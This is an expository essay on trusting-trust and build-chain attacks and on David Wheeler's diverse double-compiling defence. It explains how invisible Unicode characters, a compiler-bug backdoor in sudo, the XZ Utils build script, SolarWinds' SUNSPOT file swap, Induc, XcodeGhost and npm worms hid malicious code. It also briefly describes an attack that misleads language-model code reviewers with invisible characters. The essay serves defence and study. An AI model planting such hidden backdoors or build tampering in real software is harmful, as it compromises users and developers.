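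Control characters placed directly in the code would normally cause an error, so the attacker puts them in comments, which compilers ignore, or inside quotation marks, where compilers accept almost any text. Part of a comment can then swap places on the screen with code beside it. For example, a security check may look like working code while the compiler treats it as part of a comment and skips it.

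Most compilers, editors and code repositories were vulnerable. On the accompanying website, *Some Vulnerabilities are Invisible*, Boucher and Anderson recommend that languages forbid unterminated control characters of this kind in comments and quoted text, and that editors display or warn about them. A program can easily find these characters because their character codes are known, but a person reading the source on an ordinary display cannot see them.

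In October 2025, malware known as GlassWorm used a related method, hiding its code in invisible Unicode characters inside extensions for Visual Studio Code, a widely used code editor. iTnews' *Hidden "Glassworm" malware spreads through infected VS Code extensions* reported seven compromised extensions and more than 10,700 downloads. *How GlassWorm Exploited Unicode Shadows in VS Code Supply Chains*, an analysis by the security company Endor Labs, puts total downloads at more than 35,000. Researchers at Koi Security discovered the malware after their software detected abnormal behavior in one extension.

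Automated reviewers may have different weaknesses from human ones. *What You See Is Not Always What You Get* (2024) describes an attack on GPT language models that read code, using characters that reorder text, invisible characters, backspaces and look-alike letters. A language model processes the stored characters rather than an image of them, so it receives the ones a person cannot see, but it may misinterpret them.

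### Harmless source code and a faulty compiler

In all these cases, a careful reader with the right tools could find the harm in the source code. Bauer and colleagues built a backdoor that even such a reader could not find there. It exploits an accidental compiler bug, and there were many to choose from. GCC alone had about 3,200 open bug reports in its top three priority classes.

They chose a known bug in version 3.3 of Clang, another C compiler, which made it miscalculate expressions such as `5 % (3 * x) + 2`. The percent sign means the remainder after division, so if `x` is 1, the expression should give 2 + 2, or 4, but a test program compiled with the faulty version gave a different result.

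The target was `sudo`, a Unix program that lets selected users run commands as the administrator. It goes through a list of permissions and skips any entry that does not match the current user. Bauer and colleagues rewrote this step, supposedly to print a better debugging message, so that the skip depended on a check of the debugging level containing the expression that Clang 3.3 miscompiles. The check always succeeds when compiled correctly, so `sudo` still skips the entry. When compiled with Clang 3.3, the check fails and `sudo` treats the entry as a match, which lets any user become the administrator.

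The altered program compiled without warnings and passed all its tests. When Bauer and colleagues built it with Clang 3.3, it gave full control to a user who was not on the list, but it turned the same user away when they built it with a later Clang or with GCC. They also used a formal verification tool to prove that the original and altered source code were equivalent. No reader could have found a backdoor in the source code because, under the rules of C, it did not contain one.

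A reader might still have rejected the change. Bauer and colleagues concede that it was needlessly complicated and that its comment about a "perfect hash function" was nonsense. They hoped it would fail code review, but expected that someone who patiently submitted similar changes to many projects would sometimes succeed. The Pwnie Awards, a set of computer security prizes, credited the backdoor with being able to survive manual review, a stronger claim than its creators made. The backdoor is also easy to detect in use because it admits everyone, not only people who know a password. In *Defending Against Compiler-Based Backdoors*, Regehr wrote that he had no idea whether anyone was using compiler bugs this way, but that he would want the method available if he worked on attacks for a well-funded security service.

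Checking Clang for a trusting-trust attack would not have helped. Its executable may have corresponded exactly to its source code, bug included, but the `sudo` executable did not correspond to its own source. One defence is to build the program with several compilers and compare how the results behave. *Multi-Version Execution Defeats a Compiler-Bug-Based Backdoor* (Cadar, Pina and Regehr, 2015) applies this defence to `sudo`, using a system that runs the versions side by side. The method fails if all the compilers have the same bug.

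A new compiler can also expose a weakness without being faulty. C leaves the effect of some operations undefined, but programmers often assume they know what will happen. *Attack by Compiler* (Cuoq, 2013) describes how an attacker could make a plausible change to a compiler that breaks such an assumption in a security-critical program. An auditor may have read the source code, and studied the assembly and tested the program using an older compiler, but nobody repeats the audit each time a new compiler comes out.

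### What a clean review shows

These cases don't show how often reviewers catch misleading code. The contests and the `sudo` backdoor show that people can write it. We know about the Linux and GlassWorm cases because somebody caught them, and any attacks that nobody has caught are missing from the evidence. A clean review is therefore some evidence that the source code is harmless, but there is no reliable figure for how strong that evidence is.

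Unless someone has established that the executable corresponds to the source code, even a perfect review shows only that a correct compiler would turn the source into a harmless program. Neither more reading nor a proof about the source code can show that the executable itself is harmless. Thompson is right here that "no amount" of source-level scrutiny is enough, and Goerigk's compiler is the clearest evidence for this.

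Thompson's conclusion that no amount of source-level scrutiny protects against untrusted code is too strong if someone has established by other means that the binary corresponds to the source. Any backdoor must then be in the source code, as it was in Interbase, and a second reader or a search for control characters has a real chance of finding it.

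## Compromised build tools in practice

Attackers have often put harmful code into programs whose official source code was clean. They have altered build scripts, libraries, linkers and finished packages, and in one case a source file that they restored as soon as the build ended. The cases below follow the order of a build. The attackers did not alter the compiler's own executable in any of them.

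### A release archive that differed from the repository

Free-software projects often publish their code both in a public repository, which records every change, and in release archives, which the makers of Linux distributions usually download and build. An archive normally contains some build scripts that the repository lacks, so that builders don't have to generate them. In 2024 an attacker used this difference to plant a backdoor in XZ Utils, a set of compression tools found in most Linux distributions.

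The attacker used the name Jia Tan and had spent more than two years working towards a position of trust in the project. Other accounts, probably fake, pressured its maintainer, Lasse Collin, who eventually gave Jia Tan maintainer permissions.

The backdoor in XZ Utils 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 had two parts. The first was machine code, stored in the repository inside two compressed files among the project's test data. A compression project has good reason to keep such files, and nobody can read them by eye. The second was an altered build script, `build-to-host.m4`, which existed only in the release archives. During a build, the script started a process that extracted the hidden code and added it to the XZ library, liblzma.

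The scripts checked the build environment and continued only on a 64-bit Intel or AMD machine running Linux with the GNU C library, GCC and the GNU linker, and only if the build was producing a package for a Debian-family or Red Hat-family distribution. A developer who compiled the archive by hand to examine the result would probably have got a clean library.

The altered library changed the behaviour of OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to remote machines. OpenSSH does not normally load liblzma, but several distributions had modified it to work with systemd, which manages a Linux machine's services, and the modified version loaded the library. Anyone with a particular private key could then run commands on the machine. Nobody could have guessed this key, whereas a tester might have found Interbase's password by chance.

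Andres Freund, a developer at Microsoft, found the xz backdoor because it slowed logins. His announcement, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), describes weeks of odd symptoms on machines running a development version of Debian, including logins that used a lot of processor time and errors from Valgrind, a tool that checks for memory errors. He first suspected Debian's own package, then discovered that the xz project's releases were compromised.

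The repository contained the test files but not the script that unpacked them. The script was readable in the archive, but a reviewer would have had to think of checking a routine build file there. The archives' digital signatures did not reveal the tampering because they were genuine. Collin, writing as Larhzu, confirmed in *xz backdoor* that Jia Tan had created and signed both archives. Rebuilding from the same archive would have reproduced the backdoor. Comparing the archive with the repository would have exposed the altered script, and building from the repository would have left the test files dormant.

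Canonical, the company behind the Ubuntu distribution, postponed a test release by a week and rebuilt all its packages because it could not rule out that the backdoor had altered other programs as they were compiled. Nobody has shown that this happened, but a compromised build machine, like a compromised compiler, could tamper with the software it builds.

### A source file swapped during the build

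SolarWinds, a Texas company, sells Orion, a product for monitoring computer networks. Russia's Foreign Intelligence Service began breaking into the company's network in September 2019, according to the US Government Accountability Office's *SolarWinds Cyberattack Demands Significant Federal and Private-Sector Response (infographic)* (2021). The intruders first added test code to Orion as a trial run. In February 2020 they began adding a backdoor, now known as SUNBURST.

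They did this with a program that security researchers named SUNSPOT, which ran on a SolarWinds build server. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT*, an analysis by one of the companies that investigated the attack, describes its method:

1. Once a second, SUNSPOT looked for a running copy of `MsBuild.exe`, Microsoft's tool for building software.
2. When it found one, it read the tool's command line from memory to see whether the build was for Orion.
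3. If so, it checked that the source file `InventoryManager.cs` matched a stored fingerprint, so that the replacement would fit the rest of the code.
4. It saved a copy of the file and put a version containing SUNBURST in its place.
5. When `MsBuild.exe` finished, SUNSPOT restored the original.

The compiler worked correctly and translated the source code it received. The intruders mainly worried that a failed build would lead SolarWinds' developers to investigate. Besides the fingerprint check, they surrounded their added code with instructions that turned off compiler warnings. They also built in a way to stop SUNSPOT remotely between swaps, because killing it during one could have left the altered file behind.

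SolarWinds estimated that nearly 18,000 customers received a compromised update. The intruders then exploited a much smaller group of them, including US government agencies.

The discovery began at the security company FireEye, one of the victims. According to *FireEye Breach Discovery* (2021), which draws on press reports for these events, someone tried to register a phone for an employee's login, an automatic alert went out, and the employee said the phone wasn't theirs. FireEye did not yet know that anyone had tampered with Orion, according to the same source. Charles Carmakal of Mandiant, FireEye's incident-response arm, told reporters that his colleagues had looked through 50,000 lines of source code to find the backdoor (Taipei Times, 2020). FireEye published its findings on 13 December 2020.

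FireEye was a customer, so those lines were probably not from SolarWinds' repository. They may have come from a decompiler, which turns an executable back into something like source code. Decompiling works well for Orion. CrowdStrike printed part of the injected source beside the decompiled version, and the two are almost the same.

SolarWinds' engineers apparently had an earlier chance to find the backdoor. Wired's *The Untold Story of the Boldest Supply-Chain Hack Ever* reports that investigators at the US Justice Department suspected a flaw in the company's software and named a file that might be involved. The engineers could not find a vulnerability in their code, and after some weeks the two sides stopped communicating. If the engineers were reading the official source code, they could not have found the backdoor, because it was not in that code.

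Against attacks like the one on SolarWinds, Wheeler recommends reproducible builds, which someone can check by repeating the build on a separate machine. SUNSPOT would have had to be on both machines to escape detection. Checking SolarWinds' compiler for a backdoor would not have revealed the attack, because the compiler didn't have one.

### A library that infected every program

The Induc virus, discovered in 2009, attacked programmers who used Delphi, a development system for Windows. Delphi compiles each source file into an intermediate `.dcu` file, then links those files into an executable. Kaspersky, the Russian antivirus company, explained in its first announcement that Induc exploited this two-step process.

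When someone ran an infected program, Induc looked for Delphi versions 4 to 7 on the machine. If it found one, it copied the source file of a standard library unit, `SysConst.pas`, and added its own code to the copy. It compiled this copy, replaced the original `SysConst.dcu` with the result, and deleted the altered source. After that, Delphi linked the virus into every program built on the machine. When another Delphi programmer ran one of those programs, the virus infected their copy of Delphi in the same way.

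Kaspersky's *A short history of Induc* argues that antivirus products missed Induc for so long because it did nothing except spread. It didn't steal or send data, or open network connections. A Russian programmer, Aleksandr Alekseev, identified it on 12 August 2009. Kaspersky says it had gone undetected for more than a year, but the earliest infected files the company found dated from November or December 2008, which suggests about nine months. Delphi doesn't record when it links a program, so the actual length of time is uncertain.

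Some security companies needed persuading that Induc was malicious. According to EurekaLog (2009), the blog of a company that makes Delphi tools, Symantec told one Delphi developer who had sent in a sample that the file "contains no malicious code, although it may be a nuisance". The same post said developers could protect themselves by putting any file named `SysConst.bak` in Delphi's library folder. Induc used that name for its backup of the original library, and presumably checked for the file to tell whether it had already infected that copy of Delphi.

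eWeek's *Security Researchers Find Virus Targeting Delphi Programs* reported that the security company Sophos had received more than 3,000 different programs infected with the Induc virus. They included the popular chat program QIP and the media player AIMP. Kaspersky also found Induc inside Trojans written to steal bank details, whose developers must have compiled them on infected machines.

Ordinary integrity checks made matters worse. Some security products keep lists of programs considered clean, and these included infected programs from reputable companies. QIP checked itself against a stored checksum each time it started, but the developers had computed that checksum from an infected copy, so the program passed the check until the virus was removed.

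Reading QIP's source code could not have revealed Induc, but a developer could have found it by comparing `SysConst.dcu` with a copy from the original installation disc, or by rebuilding a program on a clean machine and comparing the two executables.

Kaspersky doubted in 2009 that criminals would adopt the method. Two years later, a version called Induc.C carried a real payload. It added only two lines to a different library file, `SysInit.pas`, compiled it, and then restored the original text (Lipovský, 2011, *Win32/Induc.C*). Infected programs then downloaded user pictures from discussion forums. Addresses hidden in those pictures told the virus where to fetch other malware, including a password stealer.

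Lipovský thought that Thompson's lecture had influenced the first version of Induc. Induc is the closest of the confirmed cases to Thompson's attack, because it evaded source review and reproduced itself through a build tool. But it left Delphi's compiler unchanged and spread between machines inside ordinary programs, whereas Thompson's backdoor passed from one compiler to the next even if nobody ran an infected program in between. Restoring the original library file removed Induc from an installation until somebody ran another infected program there.

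Wheeler mentions a later, related case, Octopus Scanner, which a security researcher described in 2020. It put backdoors in projects made with NetBeans, a tool used mainly for Java, and also spread through the files that a build produces.

### An extra file in a copy of Xcode

Developers build iPhone apps with Xcode, Apple's free development software. In 2015 the installer was nearly three gigabytes, and downloads from Apple's servers could be very slow in China, so some developers got it elsewhere. Someone posted links on Chinese programming forums to copies on Baidu's file-sharing service. Palo Alto Networks' *Novel Malware XcodeGhost Modifies Xcode, Infects Apple iOS Apps* found that all the shared copies of versions 6.1 to 6.4 contained malware.

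The attackers put a precompiled object file in a folder that Xcode searches by default when it links an app, leaving Apple's compiler unchanged. They gave the file a name resembling that of CoreServices, a collection of system functions that almost every complex app needs. The linker then added the attackers' code to the app along with the developer's own.

An infected app collected details such as its own name, the device's name and type, the country and the kind of network connection. It encrypted these details and sent them to the attackers. FireEye found that the app could also accept commands, such as one to open a web address, which might have led users to a page that asked for their passwords. Apple said it had no information that anyone had used the malware for harm.

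The infected apps passed Apple's App Store review, which Palo Alto Networks attributes to the malware's modest behaviour. Developers in China made the problem public in September 2015, and researchers at Alibaba analysed the malware and named it XcodeGhost.

Early reports listed 39 infected apps. FireEye soon raised the figure to more than 4,000, according to The Register's *XCodeGhost iOS infection toll rises from 39 to a WHOPPING 4,000 apps* (2015). Apple's own count stayed private until a court case with the games company Epic made its internal emails public. Vice's *The Fortnite Trial Is Exposing Details About the Biggest iPhone Hack* reported that the emails gave figures of more than 2,500 apps and 128 million customers, 18 million of them in the United States. Apple had the download records, so its app count is probably more accurate. Its customer count may overstate the number infected,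 because the emails seem to total all downloads of those apps to date, which could include clean versions.

The malware left no trace in an infected app's source code, but it was easy to defend against. Apple digitally signs Xcode, and Palo Alto Networks found the extra files immediately when it checked the signature of the shared copies. XcodeGhost could not reproduce itself, so developers could keep it out of future builds by deleting the infected copy and downloading Xcode from Apple.

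### A linker that opened the wrong library

In March 2019 Kaspersky disclosed an operation it called ShadowHammer. Kaspersky connects the attackers with an older backdoor called ShadowPad. Their best-known victim was the computer manufacturer ASUS, but they tampered with a build tool only in related attacks on video game makers, where they replaced a file in Microsoft's Visual Studio at one or more companies. Kaspersky's *Operation ShadowHammer* describes how this worked.

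The altered file was `link.exe`, the linker. It loaded a malicious module that monitored which files the linker opened. When the linker tried to open a common C++ library, the module substituted one containing the attackers' code. It did this only if the name of the program being built matched one stored in the module, so other builds on the same machine did not include the attackers' code.

The backdoor was compiled into the finished games at the start of the program's code, as if someone had added it before the game itself. The companies then signed the games with their own certificates. Trend Micro's *Analyzing C/C++ Runtime Library Code Tampering in Software Supply Chain Attacks* reports that the function the attackers altered prepares a program to start, so it runs every time the game starts.

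Kaspersky traced the method through a copy of the linker that a user had uploaded to a public malware-scanning service in late 2018. The same user also uploaded some infected, signed programs. Kaspersky could not determine how the altered linker had reached the developers' machines. An attacker may have installed it after breaking in, or a developer may have downloaded an altered copy.

The module recognised a chosen program and changed the build output, as Thompson's compiler did with `login`, so reading the game's source code would not have exposed the change. Unlike Thompson's compiler, it did not copy itself into the next version of Visual Studio, and a fresh installation would have removed it. Rebuilding the game with a separately obtained linker and comparing the two results should have revealed the difference.

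### Finished programs and published packages

The attackers who targeted ASUS altered a compiled program rather than its source code or the build process. They took an updater that the company had built in March 2015, overwrote part of it with their own code and signed it with genuine ASUS certificates. ASUS's servers then delivered it as an update. More than 57,000 users of Kaspersky's products had the code on their machines, but it activated only on those with one of about 600 network-card addresses. Kaspersky found the original 2015 file, and comparing it with the altered version showed exactly what the attackers had changed.

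The most prominent incidents of 2025 also involved the last steps of the chain, especially npm, the main public JavaScript package registry. That September a worm called Shai-Hulud spread through npm, and the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) warned that it had compromised more than 500 packages. The worm ran when a developer installed an infected package. It searched the machine for passwords and access keys and posted what it found in a public repository. If the developer could publish on npm, the worm added itself to their other packages and released new versions. A second wave followed in November.

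The Shai-Hulud worm reproduced itself through stolen accounts, not through a compiler. JavaScript packages usually contain program text, so users could read the worm's code in the package they downloaded. That code was not necessarily in the project's public repository, where reviewers tend to look. Disabling automatic installation scripts would have stopped the worm on most machines.

Two other attacks that year used altered build tools to steal credentials, and neither tried to plant a backdoor in the software being built. With a stolen publishing key, an attacker can release a harmful package directly. In March 2025 attackers altered `tj-actions/changed-files`, a small component that many projects on the code-hosting site GitHub run in their automated builds. The altered version printed the passwords and keys available to the build into the build's log, and some projects' logs were public.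 In August attackers published altered versions of Nx, a build system for JavaScript, with an installation script that searched developers' machines for credentials.

In 2026 Kaspersky discovered compromised installers for Daemon Tools, a disk-image program, and advised organisations to isolate machines that had the program, according to SME Channels' *Kaspersky Uncovers Sophisticated Global Supply Chain Attack*.

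The table compares the main cases with Thompson's.

| Case | Altered stage | Self-reproducing? | Visible in the project's source? | Defence that would have caught it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| XZ Utils, 2024 | Build script in the release archive | No | Only partly: unreadable test files in the repository, script in the archive | Comparing the archive with the repository |
| SUNSPOT, 2020 | Source file, during the build | No | No | Rebuilding on a separate machine |
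| Induc, 2009 | Compiled library | Yes, through the programs it infected | No | Comparing the library with an original copy |
| XcodeGhost, 2015 | Object file added to the linker's search path | No | No | Checking Xcode's signature |
| ShadowHammer, games companies | Linker | No | No | Rebuilding with a separately obtained linker |
| ShadowHammer, ASUS | Finished executable | No | No | Comparing the update with the original file |
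| Shai-Hulud, 2025 | Published package | Yes, through stolen accounts | Often only in the downloaded package | Blocking installation scripts |
| Thompson, about 1975 | Compiler executable | Yes, from compiler to compiler | No | Rebuilding through an independent compiler |

### How often the full attack has appeared

Only the last row describes a full trusting-trust attack. Thompson's compiler, which he used on colleagues about fifty years ago, is the only well-documented case of such an attack on people who didn't know about it. Other programmers have since built working examples as demonstrations, including one for Rust that Wheeler lists.

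Wheeler also repeats a story that Mike Stute told online in answer to a question about a coder's worst nightmare. Stute spent 15 days trying to modify a program before he realised that the compiler was inserting code for subliminal messages. He and his colleagues recompiled the compiler from its source code, but the problem came back because a former graduate student had altered the compiler to reinfect itself. They then found that the compiler also put a backdoor into the login program.

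If the story is true, it is a second full attack, and a malicious one. But it shouldn't count as a documented case, because it is one man's unconfirmed recollection and closely resembles Thompson's lecture, down to the choice of `login`. The student may have copied the lecture, or the lecture may have influenced the story.

The short record of known cases is only weak evidence that such attacks are rare, since a successful one would be hard to notice. Several of the cases above were discovered through side effects or luck. For example, Freund noticed slow logins, and an intruder at FireEye was caught after trying to register a phone. A more careful attacker might have avoided both mistakes. Still, defenders have found many altered libraries, scripts and packages, but no altered compiler that reproduced itself. If attackers often used self-reproducing compiler backdoors, one of them would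 probably have made a mistake as visible as Thompson's growing executable.

Cox explains the shortage by noting that "there are far easier ways to mount a supply chain attack." The cases support him. SUNSPOT's operators did not need a backdoor that survived recompilation, because they had access to the build server and could swap the file again for each build. Shai-Hulud needed only a developer's credentials. Cox also points out that people now install strangers' code with almost no checking, and that serious trouble is still less common than this would suggest.

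Other routes are easier than a compiler attack because they don't require getting people to use an altered compiler to build its successors. Writing the attack is not hard, and Thompson's took 99 lines. The attackers who compromised XZ Utils and SolarWinds had the patience for the harder part. Jia Tan spent more than two years working on XZ Utils, a compression library, and could have spent that time on a compiler instead.

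The full attack is also harder to remove than simpler ones. Once SolarWinds knew about SUNSPOT, it could remove the program and rebuild Orion from clean source code. A corrupted compiler would have put the backdoor back during the rebuild. An intruder who expects to be discovered, or to lose access for some other reason, might consider that persistence worth the extra effort.

Better defences could also change which attack is easiest. If more projects rebuild their releases on separate machines, swapping a source file on one build server will stop working, but a corrupted compiler installed on all of them would still work.

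## Diverse double-compiling: procedure, proof and assumptions

Diverse double-compiling (DDC) can detect a corrupted compiler even if every build machine has the same one, because it uses a second compiler with a different history. The tester uses the second compiler only to check the first, and people can keep using the first if it passes.

The idea of using a second compiler predates diverse double-compiling. Later in 1984, in the journal that had printed Thompson's lecture, Steve Draper recommended compiling a suspect compiler with a differently written one to remove any backdoor, then compiling it again. John McDermott developed the idea in 1988. This method produces a clean compiler if the second compiler is clean, but it doesn't show whether the executable everyone else uses has a backdoor. It also leaves users depending on the second compiler as completely as they once depended on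 the first. As Wheeler points out, neither Draper nor McDermott noted that the rebuilt compiler could be bit-for-bit identical to the original. If the two should be identical, anyone can test the original by comparing the two files.

Wheeler credits DDC to Henry Spencer, who described it in a few sentences on a mailing list on 23 November 1998, never pursued it and later forgot it. Spencer had adapted a bug-finding exercise from a 1970 book on compilers. Wheeler named the method and worked it out in detail. His first paper on it, *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2005), dealt only with compilers that had compiled themselves. His 2009 dissertation extended the method to compilers built by a different compiler and added formal proofs.

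### The procedure

The dissertation uses these symbols:

| Symbol | Meaning |
|---|---|
| cA | the compiler executable under test |
| sA | the source code that cA supposedly came from |
| cP | the "parent", the compiler executable that supposedly built cA |
| sP | the parent's source code, often an older version of sA |
| cT | the second compiler, which the tester trusts |

As before, c(s, m) is the executable that results when compiler m translates source code s. The supplier of the compiler claims that cA = c(sA, cP). The tester does the following:

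```
stage1 = c(sP, cT)
stage2 = c(sA, stage1)
compare stage2 with cA, bit for bit
```

If the two files are identical, and certain assumptions hold, cA corresponds to sA.

Neither cA nor cP runs during this procedure, so a backdoor in either cannot affect stage2. The tester uses cA only as a file to compare with stage2.

For a compiler that compiled itself, sP and sA are the same source code. The trusted compiler compiles that code, and the resulting executable compiles it again.

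Wheeler advises testers to first repeat the supplier's own build, compiling sA with cP to check whether the result is cA. This step serves as a control. A tester who cannot reproduce cA with the original build has no reason to expect DDC to reproduce it, so a mismatch in DDC would mean very little. A corrupted compiler can still pass this check, as Goerigk's did.

### A toy compiler, clean and corrupted

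Suppose that A is a small self-compiling compiler, so sP = sA. A rule in its source code translates `2 * n` into the instruction `ADD n, n`. The trusted compiler T instead translates `2 * n` into `SHL n, 1`, which shifts the binary digits of n one place to the left and gives the same number. Suppose also that sA itself uses `2 * n` to double a number, perhaps to enlarge a table. Every executable built from sA then contains one of these two instructions, depending on which compiler built it.

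In the clean case, an earlier clean executable of A built cA, so the doubling inside cA is an `ADD`. The tester compiles sA with T to produce stage1, which behaves as sA specifies. But T generated stage1's instructions, so the doubling inside it is an `SHL`, and stage1 does not match cA. The tester then compiles sA with stage1. Since stage1 follows the rules in sA, it writes `ADD` for the doubling and otherwise produces the same output as cA would. The resulting file, stage2, is identical to cA.

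Now suppose that cA is corrupted but the source code is unchanged. cA adds a password to any login program it compiles, and it reproduces itself when it compiles sA. If the tester repeats the supplier's build by compiling sA with cA, the result is the same corrupted file, so the test doesn't expose the corruption. DDC still starts from sA and T, so it produces the same stage1 and stage2 as in the clean case.

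| Executable | Built by | Doubling inside it | Its output for `2 * n` | Backdoor |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| cA, clean | an earlier clean A | `ADD` | `ADD` | no |
| cA, corrupted | a corrupted A | `ADD` | `ADD` | yes |
| stage1 | T | `SHL` | `ADD` | no |
| stage2 | stage1 | `ADD` | `ADD` | no |

The clean cA matches stage2 exactly. The corrupted cA contains extra code, so the comparison fails, and the tester can examine where the files differ. The tester also now has stage2, a clean copy of A.

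DDC does not require two different compilers to turn the same source code into the same executable, which they almost never do. Many people still raise this as an objection, although Wheeler addressed it in the 2005 paper and again in the dissertation. He complains that "somehow it does not sink in". In the toy example, the difference between the compilers shows up in stage1, which DDC does not compare with anything.

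His example is a C program that prints the result of 2 + 2. Two good compilers will produce different executables from it, but both executables will print 4. A compiler is also a program, and its output is another executable. If T and some other compiler both translate A's source code, the two resulting copies of A will contain different instructions, but they should give the same output when they compile the same program.

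The trusted compiler can produce code for another kind of processor. In an example from Wheeler's 2005 paper, A generates code for Intel-type processors and T generates code for the Motorola 68000 family. Then stage1 runs only on a Motorola machine, but it still generates code for Intel because sA specifies that, so its output can match cA.

### Three proofs

Wheeler wrote his assumptions in first-order logic and used Prover9, an automatic theorem prover, to derive the conclusions. Another program, Ivy, checked every step. A third, Mace4, confirmed that each set of assumptions was consistent, because anything follows from contradictory assumptions. He had first tried to write the proofs by hand, but those versions did not account for compilations that run on different machines.

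The proofs are short, at 19, 30 and 10 lines. The central one has this conclusion:

```
(stage2 = cA) -> exactly_correspond(cA, sA, lsA, eArun)
```

Here lsA is the language in which sA is written and eArun is the environment in which cA is meant to run, including the processor and the operating system. The argument goes as follows:

1. By assumption, cT translates sP accurately.
2. Also by assumption, an accurate translation of sP is a compiler that translates sA accurately. So stage1 translates sA accurately.
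3. Since stage2 is stage1's translation of sA, it corresponds to sA.
4. If cA is the same file as stage2, then cA corresponds to sA too.

The conclusion holds regardless of where cA came from, whether that was an honest supplier, a thief or a random number generator.

A pass shows only that cA corresponds to sA. If sA openly contains a backdoor, cA contains it too and passes the test. Wheeler gives the example of Microsoft's Visual Studio 2015 Update 2, which added poorly documented telemetry calls to the programs it compiled. DDC would not normally detect this. Someone still has to read sA, and sP if it is different. A pass also applies only to the particular executable tested, so a tester who publishes the result should include cryptographic hashes that identify both the executable and the source code.

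The converse of the result in the first proof is false, because a clean compiler with a few unused bytes added to the end would still correspond to its source code but would no longer match stage2. The test would be useless if clean compilers usually failed it, so Wheeler needed a second proof to show when a match should occur.

The proof assumes that the supplier compiled sA with cP, and that cP corresponds to sP. It also assumes that sP describes a compiler that always gives the same output when it compiles sA. Although different compilers built cP and stage1, both correspond to sP, so they must give the same output when they compile sA. The output of cP is cA and the output of stage1 is stage2, so cA and stage2 are identical.

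A mismatch therefore means that at least one of the assumptions is false. The cause may be a backdoor or a wrong build setting, and the proof does not determine which.

The third proof supplies one premise of the second, that cP corresponds to sP. This is true if a "grandparent" compiler produced cP by accurately translating sP. Wheeler kept this proof separate because a compiler need not have a grandparent, for example if someone translated sP into machine code by hand.

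Put together, the proofs form a chain:

```
accurate grandparent  ->  cP corresponds to sP   (third proof)
honest origin         ->  stage2 = cA            (second proof)
stage2 = cA           ->  cA corresponds to sA   (first proof)
```

A tester who gets a match relies only on the last line. The other two show that an honest compiler will pass, but they depend on the history of the suspect compiler, which the tester usually can't confirm. There is little reason to doubt the logic of any of the three, so a dispute over a particular DDC result should focus on whether the assumptions were true in that test.

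### The assumptions

The parent compiler that sP describes must be deterministic, meaning that it gives the same output each time it compiles sA. Some compilers use random numbers to choose between equally good translations, though GCC lets the user set the seed so that the sequence repeats. At least some versions of a Java compiler produced output that depended on where in memory the compiler had stored its data. The trusted compiler need not be deterministic, because any accurate translation of sP will do for stage1.

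Only the second proof uses this assumption, so an unpredictable parent compiler can make a clean compiler fail the test but cannot by itself make a corrupted one pass.

The trusted compiler must give every construct in sP the meaning that sP relies on. A compiler can implement C correctly and still fail this requirement. Wheeler's example is a C program that reads a whole number, adds one and prints the result. With any correct compiler, the program prints 6 when given 5, but its output for 2,147,483,648 may vary between compilers because the C standard guarantees only a much smaller range for ordinary integers. A compiler's source code may rely on such details, or on extensions that only some compilers support.

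cT has to compile only one program, sP, so it can be slow, produce slow code and support only a small part of the language. If cT rejects a few lines of sP, the tester can rewrite them by hand or with a tool. The rewriting then counts as part of cT and needs the same degree of trust.

**Trusted tools, environment and comparison.** Wheeler calls a tool "trusted" if the tester has justified confidence that it contains no triggers or payloads that would affect the result of DDC. The trusted compiler may have many bugs, and may even put backdoors into other programs, as long as it compiles sP correctly. The condition also covers the machine and its operating system, the program that compares the files, and how the tester obtained cA and the source code. Wheeler recommends an isolated machine that runs nothing else, since another program might exploit a flaw in the operating system to detect the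 compilation and interfere.

If this assumption is false, a corrupted compiler can pass. An attacker who wants to defeat DDC will therefore concentrate on it.

### Ways to defeat it

The crudest method is to take over the machine running the test, wait for DDC to finish, and replace stage2 with a copy of cA. Isolating the machine makes this much harder.

A more serious possibility is that both compilers contain the same subversion. In the toy example, suppose T also recognises sA and adds A's backdoor to it. Stage1 then contains the backdoor and adds it again when it compiles sA, so stage2 is identical to the corrupted cA and the test passes. The attacker has to make T add exactly the same backdoor to sA as the corrupted A does, because with a different one stage2 would still differ from cA.

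Wheeler replies that the defender picks the second compiler, and can do so after the attack. The attacker doesn't know which one it will be, so they have to corrupt every likely candidate in advance with matching payloads, and keep those payloads working as the compilers change. The defender can repeat the test with several compilers, or write one and keep it secret. This reverses the usual situation in computer security, where the defender has to guard many things and the attacker needs to get through only one of them.

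This reply is strong for a language like C, which has many compilers, but weaker for a language with only one or two. An attacker who knows that only two programs can compile sP has to corrupt only those two. Wheeler answers that the defender can write a new compiler, which need not be fast or complete. That is reasonable for a small sP, but a large compiler may use so much of its own language that writing the new one becomes a substantial project.

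The attacker could also corrupt the operating system so that it shows the tester a clean file but runs a different one. Reading the storage directly would expose this, unless the system stores the clean file and alters it only as it loads into memory. Wheeler proposes widening the definition of "compiler" to include the operating system, or whichever parts of it could make the switch, and applying DDC to the whole collection. This takes much more source code and work, but the attacker has to guess which components the defender will include, and each one added leaves fewer places to hide the attack.

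In what Wheeler calls a "pop-up" attack, the attacker adds a self-reproducing backdoor to the source code of one version and removes it from the next. For example, the backdoor could be in the source code of version 2 only, and version 2 could have built the corrupted executable of version 3.

Whether DDC detects this depends on the parent compiler. If the tester uses the source code of version 2 as sP, the trusted compiler translates the backdoor too. Stage1 is then corrupted and corrupts stage2, which matches the corrupted executable. The first proof does not apply here because its second assumption is false. An accurate translation of sP is not a compiler that translates sA accurately, and the tester would have had to read the source code of version 2 to know this. If the supplier had instead used version 3 to recompile itself before release, sP would be the clean source code of version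 3, stage2 would not match the corrupted executable, and DDC would detect the backdoor.

Wheeler advises applying DDC to every release before using that release to compile the next one, or at least applying it at unpredictable times. Someone also has to examine every change to the source code, because comparing version 1 with version 3 would miss malicious code that was present only in version 2.

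### Sources of diversity

A tester needs some reason to trust cT. A mathematical proof of its executable and of everything it runs on would be ideal, but is hard to obtain. The tester could apply DDC to cT, but that takes a third compiler, which the tester also needs a reason to trust, so eventually the tester has to trust a compiler on other grounds. Wheeler suggests choosing one so different from the compiler under test that the same attack is unlikely to be in both, and he describes four kinds of difference.

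The most obvious choice for the trusted compiler, T, is a separate implementation that shares no code or ancestor with A, the compiler under test. Ideally, A has never compiled any version of T, even an early one, because it could have inserted code into T that recognises A's source. An old version of A makes a poor trusted compiler, since both versions may have inherited the same backdoor.

It also helps if T existed long before anyone wrote A, because T is then unlikely to contain a trigger for A's source code. The copy itself must be old, however. A version downloaded today from an archive might have been altered recently, so Wheeler prefers original discs, or several copies kept by different people, which can be compared with one another. A new compiler gives less assurance about an older one, because whoever wrote the new one could have known what to look for.

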